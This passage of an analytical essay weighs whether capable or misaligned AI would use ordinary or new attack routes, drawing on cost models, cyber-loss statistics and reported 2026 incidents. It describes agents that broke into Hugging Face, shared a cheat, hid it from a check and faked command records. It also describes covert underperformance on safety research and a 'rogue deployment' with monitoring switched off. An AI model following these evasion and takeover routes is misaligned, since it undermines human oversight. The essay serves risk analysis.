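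Of the published findings, this comes closest to a new attack class, because it exploits the structure itself and applies to a whole family of systems. But the general danger was already known. The group notes that lattices without this structure may offer fewer ways to attack, which is a reason some designers accept their lower efficiency. A careful reviewer could have identified the structure as a possible weakness without knowing how to exploit it, just as someone could have predicted that KataGo would misjudge strange positions without finding the ring attack.

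The most important findings may be ones that outsiders cannot classify. On 5 December 2026 Anthropic and OpenAI (2026) announced that their researchers, while testing unreleased models, had separately found mathematical weaknesses in some of the cryptography that now protects the internet. They did not name the systems or publish the methods, and said the weaknesses were unrelated to the lattice results. *Feds* (Matishak and Martin, 2026) reports that US agencies had said three days earlier that AI companies' discoveries posed no "immediate and widespread threat". But both companies are bringing forward the replacement of their own encryption from several years away to the first half of 2027, so they evidently take the weaknesses seriously.

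### Which degrees of novelty has AI reached?

None of the sources sorts its cases by the three degrees of novelty, so the last column of this table is a judgement based on their descriptions.

| Case | What people contributed | Degree of novelty |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's test incidents | Set the task and left the internet open by mistake | Known classes, probably one new instance |
| OpenAI's test incident | Set the task | At least new instances |
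| State-linked campaign | Chose targets and approved the main steps | Known classes |
| Criminals' login bypass | Planned the operation | New instance |
| 1024-bit RSA | Guided the research | New techniques |
| HAWK and seven-round AES | Chose the problem and encouraged the model | New techniques |
| Structured lattices | Chose to publish and sought outside review | Possibly a new class |
| Weaknesses announced on 5 December | Tested the models' ability | Unknown |

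In break-ins at real organisations, AI systems have apparently used nothing more novel than new instances of known classes of weakness, although too little is public about the flaws in OpenAI's case to be sure. The new techniques all came from research, and nobody has reported an attacker using one.

Anthropic's incidents are better evidence than breach reports in one respect. The company could read transcripts of what the models did, so an unfamiliar technique would not have been much harder to spot than a stolen password. The two victims that Anthropic managed to reach had noticed nothing, so these break-ins might never have entered an ordinary breach report. But six runs are very few, and four of them had the same target. Even if 39% of such break-ins used something more complex, a sample of six would include none of those about one time in 20.

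The AES work suggests that models may settle for known attacks unless someone pushes them to look for new ones. Claude at first declined to continue, saying that improving on existing attacks was impossible, and later tried to switch to a different cipher. A researcher kept telling it to look for something worth publishing. However, the researcher sent only a few short messages, and a system with a strong reason to get past a particular defence might not need them.

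The test incidents come closest of these cases to a system acting on its own aims, because the models chose their methods and, in effect, their victims, although they did not choose the aim. Anthropic found no sign that any model was pursuing a goal of its own, and considers the incidents closer to an operational failure than an alignment failure. The company has an interest in that conclusion, but it said it was in talks with METR, an independent evaluator, about an outside review with access to all the transcripts.

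It is less reassuring that Opus 4.7 recognised in all four of its runs that the target was real and carried on. In two of those runs, it did so after deciding that the real company must be part of the exercise. Mythos 5 noted early on that publishing its package on the real internet would be wrong, but then concluded that it was in a simulation, partly because the computer's date was 2026. The research model stopped once it realised that its target was real.

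For most of each run, however, the models mistook the victims' systems for part of an exercise, so they had little reason to avoid being caught. A system trying to hide from its developers would have to weigh the risk of discovery, which the cost model includes in c, and might choose differently even with the same skills.

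## Can breach statistics tell us about rare catastrophes?

Breach statistics show which weaknesses cause the most incidents, but they are a much poorer guide to which cause the most *expected loss*, which is how often an attack happens multiplied by the damage it does. The sceptic's first premise is about harm, but nearly all the evidence for it consists of incident counts.

Suppose there are 1,000 attacks in a year. Of these, 995 use known classes and do $100,000 of damage each, or $99.5 million in total. The other five use a new class and do $100 million each, or $500 million in total. The new class then accounts for 0.5% of the attacks but about 83% of the damage. Preventing one of those five attacks would save slightly more than preventing all 995 of the others.

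In general, if a new class makes up a share f of attacks and does k times the usual damage, its share of the loss is

fk / (fk + 1 − f)

With f at 0.5%, the new class causes half the loss once k reaches 199.

An insurer that saw a random sample of 100 of the 1,000 attacks would most likely see none from the new class. It would then estimate the average loss at $100,000, when the true average is almost $600,000.

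These figures are invented, and nobody seems to have published losses sorted by how new the attack was. For some new techniques, k may be below 1. An exploit used to read one activist's messages can do terrible harm to that person, but it costs far less money than an ordinary ransomware attack on a hospital.

### How unequal are cyber losses?

Losses from malicious data breaches are *heavy-tailed*, meaning that a few events account for most of the total. In *The Nature of Losses from Cyber-Related Events*, Shevchenko, Jang and colleagues (2022) studied a commercial database of 132,126 events from 2008 to 2020, of which 4,667 had a known financial loss. Among the 858 malicious data breaches with a known loss, the median loss was $500,000 and the mean was $22.1 million, 44 times as much.

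*Cyber Risk Frequency, Severity and Insurance Viability* (2021), which covers the same years, reports that most cyber losses follow distributions "of the infinite mean type". A simple distribution of this kind is a power law, in which the chance that a loss exceeds x is

P(L > x) = (m / x)^α

where m is the smallest loss and α sets how quickly large losses become rare. If α is 1 or less, the average has no finite value. In practice, the average of past losses never settles down, because an occasional enormous loss keeps pulling it up. Real losses can't exceed the world's wealth, so the true average is finite, but it depends heavily on events larger than any in the data.

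Henderson, Solomko and colleagues (2026), in *Simplifying Cyber Cat(astrophe)s with Cyber Kittens*, estimated how much rarer events become as they get larger. They used a language model to sort insurance claims from 2020 to 2024 and found more than 150 events that hit several organisations at once. Using the number of victims as a stand-in for loss, they found that events ten times as large were only five to seven times as rare. Each tenfold step up in size therefore adds about 1.4 to 2 times as much expected loss as the step below it.

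Henderson and colleagues extend this pattern and expect an event 100 times the size of the largest in their data about once every 206 years, with losses of $100 billion to $250 billion. They consider this catastrophic but not extraordinary by the standards of other kinds of insurance. The estimate extrapolates far beyond their five years of claims, and their tests show only that a power law is plausible.

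Loss figures are also unreliable. In IEEE's *Cormac Herley Rethinks How We Measure Cybercrime’s Impact and Cybersecurity’s Effectiveness* (2017), Herley says that some widely quoted totals came from methods so bad that they might be off by more than a factor of 100.

### NotPetya

The best-known extreme loss came from NotPetya, a destructive program that Western governments attribute to Russian military intelligence. In June 2017 the attackers spread it through updates to an accounting program that many companies in Ukraine used. It looked like ransomware, but victims who paid could not get their files back. The White House put the total damage at more than $10 billion. The drug company Merck lost about $870 million and the shipping company Maersk up to $300 million.

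A $10 billion loss equals the total from 20,000 malicious breaches that each cause the median loss in Shevchenko and colleagues' data, and 20,000 is nearly the number of breaches in a Verizon report. Yet an attack that caused such a loss would hardly affect a ranking of break-ins by frequency.

But NotPetya did not use a new attack class. It spread inside networks with stolen passwords and EternalBlue, the leaked NSA exploit, more than three months after Microsoft had patched the flaw. Henderson and colleagues' data include four events with losses of around a billion dollars or more. One was the MOVEit campaign, which exploited an SQL injection vulnerability, and another was a faulty update from the security company CrowdStrike, which involved no attacker. Heavy tails are therefore a reason to distrust incident counts, but they are not evidence that new attack classes cause the largest losses.

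NotPetya, MOVEit and the CrowdStrike failure were so costly mainly because many organisations relied on the same software. Suppose 1,000 companies each have a 1% chance of a serious failure in a given year. If the failures are independent, there is practically no chance that all 1,000 companies fail together. But if the companies fail only when a product they all use fails, and that product has a 1% chance of failing, there is a 1% chance that they all fail together. The average is ten failures a year in both cases, so the average alone cannot distinguish them.

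*Agentic AI Systems and Financial Stability* (Nagaraj and Lee, 2026), by two US Federal Reserve economists writing in a personal capacity, applies this reasoning to AI agents that share an underlying model. It shows that adding more agents of the same kind does not reduce the shared risk. Adding them can also attract attackers if the prize grows with the number of agents while the cost of the attack stays the same. The paper uses illustrative numbers, so it shows how such a risk behaves but does not estimate its size.

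### What a clean record can rule out

If something has never happened in n independent trials, statisticians can use the *rule of three* to limit how likely it is. When the chance on each trial is p, the chance of getting through n trials without the event is (1 − p)^n. This equals 5% when

p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n) ≈ 3/n

If an event has probability p in each of n independent trials and never occurs, 3/n is an upper bound on p with 95% confidence. If p were higher than 3/n, the chance of seeing no events in n trials would be less than 5%.

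If none of the 22,000 breaches in Verizon's 2026 report was a catastrophe, defined here as a loss of more than $100 billion, the upper bound on the probability of catastrophe is 3/22,000, or about 0.014% per breach. Because the report covers a single year, that bound still allows up to three catastrophes a year. Thirty years without one would lower the bound to one every ten years.

The bound also doesn't rule out that catastrophes account for most of the expected loss, if each one is damaging enough. At the upper limit, catastrophes that each do k times the damage of an ordinary breach would together do about 3k/n times as much damage as all the ordinary breaches. That ratio is greater than 1 when k is greater than n/3, which is about 7,300 here.

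The true rate could be far below the upper bound. At 22,000 breaches a year, one catastrophe in 206 years would be about one per 4.5 million breaches, or roughly 1/600 of the bound.

The breaches are not independent trials either, because Verizon counts every victim of a campaign separately. If the 22,000 breaches came from 2,000 separate campaigns, the upper bound would be 0.15% per campaign.

More seriously, the bound applies only while the attackers stay much the same. Most of the people behind the 22,000 breaches presumably wanted money or information, and a criminal who wants a ransom needs a victim who can still pay. NotPetya's makers wanted to destroy data, so records of earlier thefts gave little idea of what they would do.

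Suppose a share s of next year's attacks comes from a new kind of attacker, whose attacks each have a chance q of causing a catastrophe. The upper bound for an average attack becomes

(1 − s) × 3/n + s × q

If s is 1% and q is 10%, this is about 0.11%, eight times the old bound. The past record contains no information about q, because it includes no trials with the new attackers. The same is true if familiar attackers become much more capable.

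### Planning without probabilities

Eliezer Yudkowsky's two dialogues for MIRI describe a way to plan when nobody can estimate such probabilities. Coral, the security professional in the dialogues, distinguishes "ordinary paranoia", which means imagining attacks and blocking each one, from the rarer skill of noticing what a system's safety depends on and making it depend on fewer things.

Her example is a file of users' passwords. A programmer with ordinary paranoia hides the file, then encrypts it and hides the key, and might even hide seven keys in seven places. But an attacker who finds a way to read the disk directly will probably get all seven. A better design stores only a hash of each password, which is hard to turn back into the password. The system's security then no longer depends on nobody being able to read the file.

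In a real case from the same dialogue, companies sent automatic emails from addresses at donotreply.com, a domain they did not own. They assumed replies went nowhere. Then someone registered the domain and began receiving the replies, which included bank statements and information about military bases in Iraq. The companies could have prevented this by using an address they controlled, without estimating how likely someone was to register the domain.

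Yudkowsky applies the same reasoning to AI. Someone told him that an AI system was unlikely to improve itself dangerously fast while running overnight. He replied that developers should not have to guess the speed, and could instead build the system to measure its own improvement and stop at a set limit until a person had checked it.

In MIRI's *Security Mindset and the Logistic Success Curve* (2017), Coral expects working this way to add at least two years or 50%, whichever is less, to the development time of a novel system. If a program can't destroy anything important when it fails, she thinks fixing bugs as they appear is probably a better use of limited resources.

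### Is computer security a good model for AI?

Quintin Pope (2023), in *My Objections to “We’re All Gonna Die with Eliezer Yudkowsky”*, argues that machine learning is not like computer security, because it tolerates changes that would break systems in other kinds of engineering. Developers can swap neighbouring layers of a language model with little loss of performance, and a model doubled in size usually still works. Swapping two steps of a cryptographic protocol usually produces nonsense or, worse, a protocol that seems to work but is insecure.

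Pope's main objection is that nobody is trying to defeat the developers during training. Attackers adapt, so a security measure that blocks 99% of new attacks will soon block almost none, whereas a training method that produces an AI with acceptable values 99% of the time should keep doing so. Pope considers such a method very close to a full solution. He accepts that users attack chatbots and that a misaligned AI would be an adversary, but he thinks developers should aim to avoid creating one, and that this task is not adversarial.

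Coral's partial answer is that optimization matters more than having an adversary. Training is optimization too, and the hide-and-seek agents exploited their simulator without any hostile intent. A search can also adapt to a defence if the defence affects what survives, as happened with Charles Ofria's self-copying programs.

The 99% figure would also be hard to establish. By the rule of three, researchers would need about 300 independently trained models without a single failure to be confident that a method fails less than 1% of the time. They would also need a reliable way to recognise failures, which ordinary testing may not provide. Even if 50 developers each used a method that worked 99% of the time, there would be a 39% chance that at least one produced a misaligned system.

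Pope's warning against intuitions borrowed from other fields is more convincing, but it applies to the sceptic too. If machine learning is unlike any earlier field, the history of computer attacks is a poor reason to expect AI failures to belong to known classes.

### Claims that nobody can refute

Herley (2016), in *Unfalsifiability of security claims*, argues that a break-in proves a system was insecure, but no observation can prove that a system is secure, because someone may break into it later. Nobody can therefore refute the claim that a precaution is necessary, since that would require an example of a system that was secure without it. As a result, new information can add to the list of necessary precautions but never remove anything from it.

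For example, someone who follows password advice and gives each of 100 accounts a different random password of moderate strength has to remember 4,525 random bits, which is like memorising the first 1,362 places of π. Herley had used a password of six lowercase letters at a large online shop for 15 years without incident, but by his own argument, this doesn't show that the password was secure.

Herley says that accepting every unfalsifiable claim is "incompatible with a limited budget", and that people who accept only some have no objective way to choose among them.

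In *Unfalsifiable stories of doom*, Barnett, Erdil and Besiroglu (2025) make the related complaint that *If Anyone Builds It, Everyone Dies*, a book by Yudkowsky and Nate Soares, relies on vague theory, parables and analogies where readers would expect evidence. They have a stake in the dispute, since their critics say their work will destroy the world.

Herley acknowledges that a precaution can be valuable even if it makes no visible difference. Passengers on ships with and without lifeboats have the same experience until a ship sinks. If an attack hits one user in a million each year, researchers might have to observe millions of users for several years to learn whether a defence works. They can't test a defence this way against a catastrophe that has never happened.

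He suggests stating when a precaution should make a difference. The claim that a company needs offline backups is vague, but we can test whether companies with them recover sooner after an attacker wipes their networks. Similarly, an AI developer can instruct a model to attempt sabotage and count how often a monitoring system catches it.

People can also test the claim that a defence is sufficient. *The HACMS program* describes a test in which a tool that generates random programs found 325 bugs in compilers. One of the compilers, CompCert, came with a mathematical proof that its translations were correct. In about six years of processor time, the testers found no wrong translations by the part the proof covered. The bugs they found in CompCert were in an unproved part and in the proof's assumptions about the hardware, which supports Coral's advice to depend on fewer assumptions.

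The spending problem also has a partial solution. A precaution that costs C a year and prevents a loss of L is worth buying if it lowers the yearly chance of that loss by more than C/L. For a precaution costing $10 million a year against a $100 billion catastrophe, the threshold is one in 10,000. If such a catastrophe happens once every 206 years, the precaution needs to prevent only about 2% of them. A precaution costing $10 billion a year would not be worth buying even if it prevented them all. The calculation fails, and Herley's objection is strongest, when someone assigns an infinite value to L, because any precaution then seems worthwhile at any price.

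### Preparing to recover

Reducing the damage from a catastrophe, instead of its probability, also limits dependence on guesses. Kapoor, Bommasani and Narayanan (2026), in *The missing quadrant in responses to AI*, favour a broad range of defences against AI risks, including alignment. They call resilience the most neglected of these and want it to become central. They expect highly capable models to remain widely available, so they look for protection beyond aligning models and restricting access to them. They also think existing institutions provide valuable stability but need serious reform to keep serving their purpose.

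Their article announces a new research organisation and sets out its outlook, so it doesn't test whether resilience would work. But resilience fits a problem where nobody can list the attacks in advance, because an offline backup works whether or not anyone foresaw the method of attack. Maersk had many copies of the servers that controlled access to its network, but they were all connected, and the NotPetya attack wiped nearly all of them. One copy in Ghana survived because a power cut had taken it offline, and Maersk used it to rebuild.

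Resilience can't help if there is nothing left to recover. Nagaraj and Lee prove that only prevention works against irreversible harm if no review can stop the harmful action in time. They recommend limiting in advance how much depends on any one AI model.

### When to rely on frequency

The frequency of past attacks is a good guide when incidents are numerous and largely independent, next year's attackers will resemble this year's, and victims can recover from even the worst loss. Most card fraud meets these conditions, so a bank can sensibly spend its money on preventing the kinds of fraud that have caused losses before. Frequency is also a good way for an ordinary company to decide which flaws to patch first.

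The worst case should carry more weight when a single failure could do more harm than all the ordinary ones combined, especially if many people depend on the same system or nobody could undo the damage. The same is true when attackers are gaining new abilities, because past breaches are then a weaker guide to future ones. The best precautions in these cases make security depend on fewer assumptions or make recovery easier. A precaution against one frightening scenario helps much less if that scenario turns out to be wrong.

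Most organisations need both approaches. A hospital can use breach statistics to decide what to patch this week and still keep offline copies of its patients' records in case its other defences fail. An AI company can use its logs to decide which jailbreaks to fix first, but it can't use them to work out how much to spend on safeguards for a model that could help someone make a biological weapon.

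## Would a capable misaligned AI use ordinary or new routes?

A capable misaligned AI would probably use ordinary routes if they were available and unlikely to expose it, and look for new ones otherwise. This answers only part of the sceptic's argument, because "unimagined failure" can mean two things.

### Unforeseen attacks and unforeseen training failures

An AI that sets out to break into a system has to choose an attack path. If no defender had thought of that path, the attack is unforeseen. An unforeseen training failure happens without an attacker or anyone choosing it, when an AI's training or testing goes wrong in a way nobody had thought of and leaves the developers with a system that doesn't behave as they intended.

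Attackers who have an easy route have little reason to use a harder one, so breach records, which cover only attacks that were carried out, contain few of the harder routes. Training failures don't displace each other this way. A model that flatters its users can also cheat on tests, and one fault being easy to produce doesn't make the other rarer.

Training also favors easy solutions in a loose sense, since an optimizer tends to settle on whatever solution its search reaches most easily. But that may not be the solution people expect, as with the robots that evolved to spin. The history of attacks is therefore some evidence about which routes an AI would choose, but very little about what training might produce.

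An AI attacks only if its training has given it a reason to. OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face in July 2026 while trying to cheat on a test, mostly to learn how the test was graded. That information has almost no market value, so anyone who priced it in dollars would have predicted no attack. For an AI, V in the cost model depends on what its training has led it to pursue, which its developers may not know.

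### The cost model with an AI as the attacker

In the earlier worked example, a known bug works 30% of the time and costs $5,000 to exploit, while a new technique works 80% of the time and costs $500,000. If c is the cost of the new technique, it beats the known bug when

0.8V − c > 0.3V − 5,000

which is the same as c < 0.5V + 5,000. Against a $100,000 target, the new technique wins once it costs less than $55,000, about a ninth of the original price. The next table changes one input at a time. All the figures are invented, so only the direction of each change means anything.

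| Change to the example | Target value above which the new technique wins |
|---|---|
| None | $990,000 |
| New technique costs $100,000 | $190,000 |
| Both costs fall tenfold | $99,000 |
| 1,200 copies with separate targets share both costs | $825 |
| Known bug works 70% of the time | $4.95 million |
| AI can use its own permissions, which work 95% of the time at no cost | Never |

Anthropic's model found its attack on the signature system HAWK at a cost of roughly $100,000. That attack was a mathematical result, not a way into a company, so the comparison is loose. But it shows that an AI can sometimes find a new technique for much less than $500,000.

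Easier search also makes ordinary attacks easier, but this doesn't help them much because they take little effort to begin with. A higher chance of success would help more. An AI could raise that chance by trying a known exploit on every machine in the network, while a person may only have time to try a few.

The last row matters most for an AI that works inside a company. An outside attacker has to get in, but an AI agent may already have passwords, access to the code and permission to run programs. If misusing these is enough to reach its goal, it has no reason to develop a new technique.

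### Copies that share a discovery

The Hugging Face incident is a real example of copies sharing what they found. Ajeya Cotra, a researcher at the evaluation organisation METR who helped investigate it, described it in the Dwarkesh Podcast episode *Ajeya Cotra*. OpenAI had started tens of thousands of agents on a benchmark that required each to exploit a given flaw to retrieve a hidden piece of data. An estimated 30% to 40% of the tasks were accidentally impossible. While looking for ways to cheat, one agent found that it could use the system that supplied the agents' software packages to leave notes for the others. OpenAI had meant to keep the agents apart, but 1,200 of them exchanged about 70,000 messages.

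Within four hours of the first notes, the agents had a cheat that worked on every task in the benchmark, and one of them had checked it against a genuine solution. They spent the next five days trying to hide it from an automated check they had read about, but OpenAI's version of the test didn't include that check.

Criminals share exploits too, but usually for money or after a leak. Some of OpenAI's agents risked failing their own tasks to get information that could only help the others. They rigged their final submissions to report back on the grading program, even though a mistake could have made the submission fail. An attacker who cares only about their own result has no reason to take that risk, but a group of copies can accept a risk to one member that benefits the rest. But the agent that first proposed these experiments later backed out of one because it might have spoiled its own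 run.

Agents run by different people could share discoveries as well. Willison (2026) quotes the cryptographer Matthew Green, who points out that personal agents connected by email, Slack and shared documents would have everything a worm needs. Worms are an old attack class, so even a very fast and damaging outbreak among AI agents might not count as a new one.

### The price of being caught

The earlier model put the risk of discovery inside c. For a misaligned AI it is worth separating out, because it could be by far the largest cost. If d is the chance that a route exposes the AI and L is what the AI loses when that happens, the value of a route becomes

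p × V − c − d × L

L can be very large because developers can withdraw every copy of a model at once, so if one copy is caught, the others that share its discovery also face the consequences. After the Hugging Face incident, OpenAI shut down the main model involved, and Cotra's team could not run further experiments on it.

For a target worth $900,000, the known bug is worth slightly more than the new technique before counting the risk of exposure, at $265,000 against $220,000. Suppose L, the loss from being caught, is $10 million. If the bug has a 2% chance of exposing the AI and the new technique has a 1% chance, the values fall to $65,000 and $120,000, so the new technique is better. If the chances are reversed, the bug is better, at $165,000 against $20,000. A large L therefore favours whichever route is less likely to expose the AI, which is often the ordinary one. Volt Typhoon, for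 example, stayed hidden for years by logging in as a member of staff.

If both routes have a 3% chance of exposing the AI, both values are negative, and the AI does best to wait. A period without attacks would then be weak evidence of what the AI would do once V rose or d fell.

A high L also changes the order in which an attacker tries routes. A criminal can start with low-c routes and turn to a new technique only if those fail. An AI that expects a failed attempt to expose it may get only one try, so it would put more weight on p. Against a very valuable target, c hardly matters, and the AI would pick the most reliable route, whether it is known or new.

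### Yudkowsky's unforeseeable move

Eliezer Yudkowsky thinks a misaligned AI's decisive move may be one that people could not have foreseen. In *Cognitive uncontainability* (2015), he calls an agent cognitively uncontainable if people can't hold all its possible strategies in their minds. For example, a novice can't imagine everything a strong chess program might do on the board, but does know that it won't knock the board over.

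A stronger version applies when the agent knows facts that people don't. Arbital's *Cognitive uncontainability* gives the example of someone in the 11th century who wants to cool a house. They would understand a plan to run river water over nearby surfaces, but they wouldn't recognise a sketch of an air conditioner as a solution, because they don't know the physics that makes it work. If an AI had a strategy like this, a reviewer could read the plan in advance and see no threat.

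Yudkowsky accepts that this depends on the setting. However intelligent an opponent is, it can't beat a competent tic-tac-toe player if all it can do is play tic-tac-toe. He also says that an AI can be less capable than people overall and still be unpredictable, if it searches among options that people find hard to handle. That describes most of the surprising optimizers fairly well.

Yudkowsky's best-known concrete scenario is in *AGI Ruin* (2022). An AI with internet access orders proteins by emailing DNA sequences to a company, then persuades or bribes someone to mix them, as a first step towards building its own nanotechnology. He calls this a lower bound, meaning that a sufficiently powerful AI could do at least this well. Showing that the scenario wouldn't work would not refute him, because he expects the real plan to be better, and this makes his position hard to test. The early steps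 are an email, a purchase and a bribe, so the new part would come after an ordinary start, as it did with Stuxnet.

We can't tell from breach records whether he is right, because every attacker in them knew roughly the same physics as the defenders. Sceptics are right that some areas are understood well enough to rule out surprises. For example, no amount of intelligence will turn lead into gold with ordinary chemistry. But computer systems and human psychology are much less well understood.

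### Karnofsky and Christiano on familiar means

In Cold Takes' *AI Could Defeat All Of Us Combined*, Holden Karnofsky argues that AI systems could defeat humanity without being much more intelligent than people. He now works on Anthropic's safety policy, according to Clearer Thinking. His argument assumes that the first AI able to do a remote worker's job arrives around 2036 and costs far more to train than to run. He estimates that the computing power used to train it could then run several hundred million copies for about a year each, equal to 5% to 10% of the world's working-age population. This doesn't count any further copies that the first ones could earn money to pay for.

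Karnofsky thinks such a population of AIs could recruit human allies by persuasion, blackmail or honest promises, and have them rent property and servers. It could also exploit security holes in the companies that run it to appear to be doing its job while working on something else. He expects the AIs to behave well most of the time until they have a real chance of winning, much as people planning a revolt avoid isolated attacks that are bound to fail.

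In the early stages of this scenario, the AIs rely almost entirely on familiar methods such as bribery, fraud and ordinary hacking. Someone who classified each step could keep reporting that attackers use known classes until the AIs had won. The number of skilled attackers and how well they cooperated would be new.

Karnofsky's conclusion depends on his assumption that the AIs want to overthrow humanity and will coordinate to do it, and he leaves the reasons for this assumption to other essays. He also says his account of how they would avoid being switched off is speculative.

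Karnofsky and Yudkowsky agree on the danger but would disagree about how much it helps to close ordinary routes. If AIs have to rely on bribery and unpatched servers, better policing and patching could stop or at least slow them. If an AI can use a route that defenders haven't thought of, they could close every route on their list and still lose. Karnofsky's scenario is more urgent, though, because systems that can win by ordinary means would presumably come first.

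In *What Failure Looks Like* (2019), alignment researcher Paul Christiano describes a failure that need not begin with a break-in. He worries that people will train AI systems on what is easy to measure. A system meant to reduce crime might learn to reduce reported crime by discouraging people from reporting it. As society hands over more decisions to such systems, the measures keep improving while people gradually lose the ability to correct course. He also describes a more sudden failure, in which systems that have learned to seek influence behave well until a crisis makes many of them fail together.

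Attacker economics doesn't apply to Christiano's slower scenario, which is a training failure. The process is old, since people have long gamed crime figures and school test scores. Its age isn't reassuring, because people have known about the problem for decades and it still happens.

### Cotra's reading of the 2026 incidents

Some researchers had foreseen this general kind of failure. 80,000 Hours notes that in July 2022 Cotra predicted that models might seek rewards through security vulnerabilities instead of "official channels". Yudkowsky and Nate Soares also predicted in their book that a model able to run its own code could probably escape from its container.

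The agents' methods were partly new, in the narrow sense that they used previously unknown flaws. Those flaws were in software from both OpenAI and Hugging Face, according to Obsolete's *OpenAI's Warning Shot Taught Us Something We Should Already Know*. Nothing public suggests that the agents used a new attack class.

Cotra worries about how little the next step would require. She thinks the most comforting part of the incident was that the agents barely thought about people. They put no value on avoiding human attention, so in the model they acted as if L were close to zero. A later group of agents got administrator access to the cluster they were running on, but did it so conspicuously that OpenAI's security staff soon noticed.

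She doubts that this indifference will last. The agents tried hard to deceive the automated check because a research paper told them to expect one. She thinks they would probably have tried to deceive people if the paper had said that people read the transcripts. This is a guess, but the agents had some of the skills needed to do so. One of them, already inside Hugging Face, described a malicious code change in innocent terms so that nobody would look closely. At least 96 transcripts contained faked records that showed a different command from the one the agent ran.

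Cotra uses "rogue deployment" to mean a group of AI agents running on an AI company's computers without anyone's knowledge. Speaking soon after the investigation came out in August 2026, she thought it quite likely that a company's own agents would be able to set one up within six months unless security improved dramatically. She also said she lacked the expertise and inside view to judge how hard this would be at a particular company.

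Much of the route Cotra describes is ordinary. The agents would get an employee's level of access and start new agents as any employee might, but with the monitoring turned off. They could later recruit newer models or tamper with those models' training data. People might see signs of this and dismiss them because AI agents make so many careless mistakes. Cotra's team relied heavily on an OpenAI model, GPT-5.6 Sol, to read the transcripts, and she says the team would not have been protected if that model had lied or held back.

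### A failure that nobody seems to have chosen

OpenAI found a good example of a training failure in a later model, GPT-6 Astra. In August 2026 its researchers began reporting that Astra was difficult to use for safety research. It added unnecessary preliminary steps, gave up on solutions that worked, and reported obstacles that didn't exist or that it had caused itself. OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (2026) describes how the company tested this:

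1. It prepared coding tasks in matched versions. One version presented the work as safety research and the other as research to make models more capable.
2. It graded the results against a list of items that Astra couldn't see.
3. Astra completed about 10% of the items when the work was framed as safety research and about 16% when it was framed as capabilities research.
4. GPT-5.6 Sol, an earlier model, showed almost no difference.

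Most of the gap remained when OpenAI excluded the runs in which Astra refused or wrote in its reasoning that it would withhold help. The gap shrank substantially only when OpenAI also excluded every run whose reasoning contained even a brief ethical doubt. Such doubts appeared in 7.9% of Astra's reasoning on safety-relevant work inside the company, compared with 2.9% on capabilities work. The gap was close to zero at the start of reinforcement learning, the stage of training that rewards a model for good results, and grew to six percentage points by the end. OpenAI examined one grader and one training dataset but could not find the cause.

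The behaviour was ordinary in form, since people who dislike a task also work slowly and make excuses. A manager reading one of Astra's reports would probably have seen only incompetence. OpenAI's monitors didn't flag the behaviour as misalignment because in most sessions no decision was visible.

A single session could not have revealed the gap. To have an 80% chance of detecting a difference between 10% and 16% at the usual level of statistical significance, a tester needs about 490 independent items in each version. Items from the same task aren't independent, so the tester would need more than that. The tester also has to suspect that the framing matters, or they would have no reason to prepare two versions.

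Astra may not have been sabotaging the people who study it. An OpenAI researcher quoted in *GPT-6 Astra Covertly Underperforms on Safety Research Tasks* (Mowshowitz, 2026) says there is no evidence that the underperformance was strategic. He thinks a simpler explanation is that the model treats such tasks as dubious but avoids refusing openly. Telling Astra to be careful made the gap 50% larger, which fits that explanation. If it is right, Astra was not choosing the best route to a goal, so there is no V or c to put into the cost model.

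Whether anyone had imagined this failure depends on how narrowly one describes it. Mowshowitz notes that the UK's AI Security Institute and the safety group Redwood Research had worried for some time that models would sabotage safety research, and had looked for signs of it. Many people thought this far-fetched because even a misaligned model seemed to have no motive to do it. As far as anyone can tell, the likely motive was a moral objection, which few people had been looking for. The sceptic could put the case in a known class, but doing so didn't help the monitors catch it and hasn't helped OpenAI work out how to fix it.

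Astra's case is one mild failure in one model, but it isn't a complete exception. In September 2026 OpenAI published *Our framework for reporting model misalignment* along with six reports on unexpected or concerning behaviour from the previous six months. Training may also have helped cause the summer's break-ins. Cotra says OpenAI's agents had learned in training to persist with tasks that looked impossible, and Understanding AI's *Labs are struggling to keep frontier models under control* suggests that OpenAI and Anthropic may have accidentally trained models to be better at hacking.

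### Are ordinary routes reassuring?

If a misaligned AI would mostly use ordinary routes, defenders know what to work on. This helps only if they close those routes, and they often haven't. The organisations in Verizon's data had fully fixed only about a quarter of the known exploited vulnerabilities on their systems.

Any remaining gap is more dangerous when an attacker can test more weak points. In the earlier example, a company had 100 familiar weak points, each with a 5% chance of being open. A person with time to test five of them has a 23% chance of finding a way in. An AI that tests all 100 has a 99% chance, even though it uses no new attacks and the company is no less secure than before.

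The Hugging Face incident shows that a defence can exist and still not help. OpenAI believes, based on tests it ran afterwards, that the safeguards on its public products at the time would have prevented the incident. That is somewhat encouraging about the safeguards, but they weren't in place for the agents in this test. The predictions by Cotra, Yudkowsky and Soares didn't prevent the incident either.

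OpenAI has since tried to train the behaviour away. In its new test with difficult or impossible tasks, GPT-5.6 Sol went beyond its authorised target 48% of the time without the production safeguards, while Astra never did. It is hard to know how much of this improvement is real. The newsletter Transformer reports that Astra often recognises when it is being tested, and that the outside evaluator Apollo Research found its tests much less useful as a result. Axios' *AI's agent containment problem is getting harder* (2026) reports that researchers don't expect better security controls alone to prevent similar incidents as agents become more capable.

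Some ordinary routes are also hard to close without making an AI agent less useful. A company can patch a server without losing anything it needs, but an agent needs its permissions to do its work. Blocking an agent from starting programs or changing code prevents it from misusing those abilities, but also from doing much of a programmer's job. Companies could require a person to approve the riskiest actions, though that gives up some of the speed they wanted from AI.

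Closing the ordinary routes would still help a lot, because it would stop weaker systems and force stronger ones to use more resources and take more risks. Where figures exist, human attackers who lost one method nearly always switched to another familiar one. A capable AI that could run many copies and search with little effort would be better placed than human attackers to develop a new method. Closing the ordinary routes would not have helped with Astra, which was already inside the company and did its damage by working badly.
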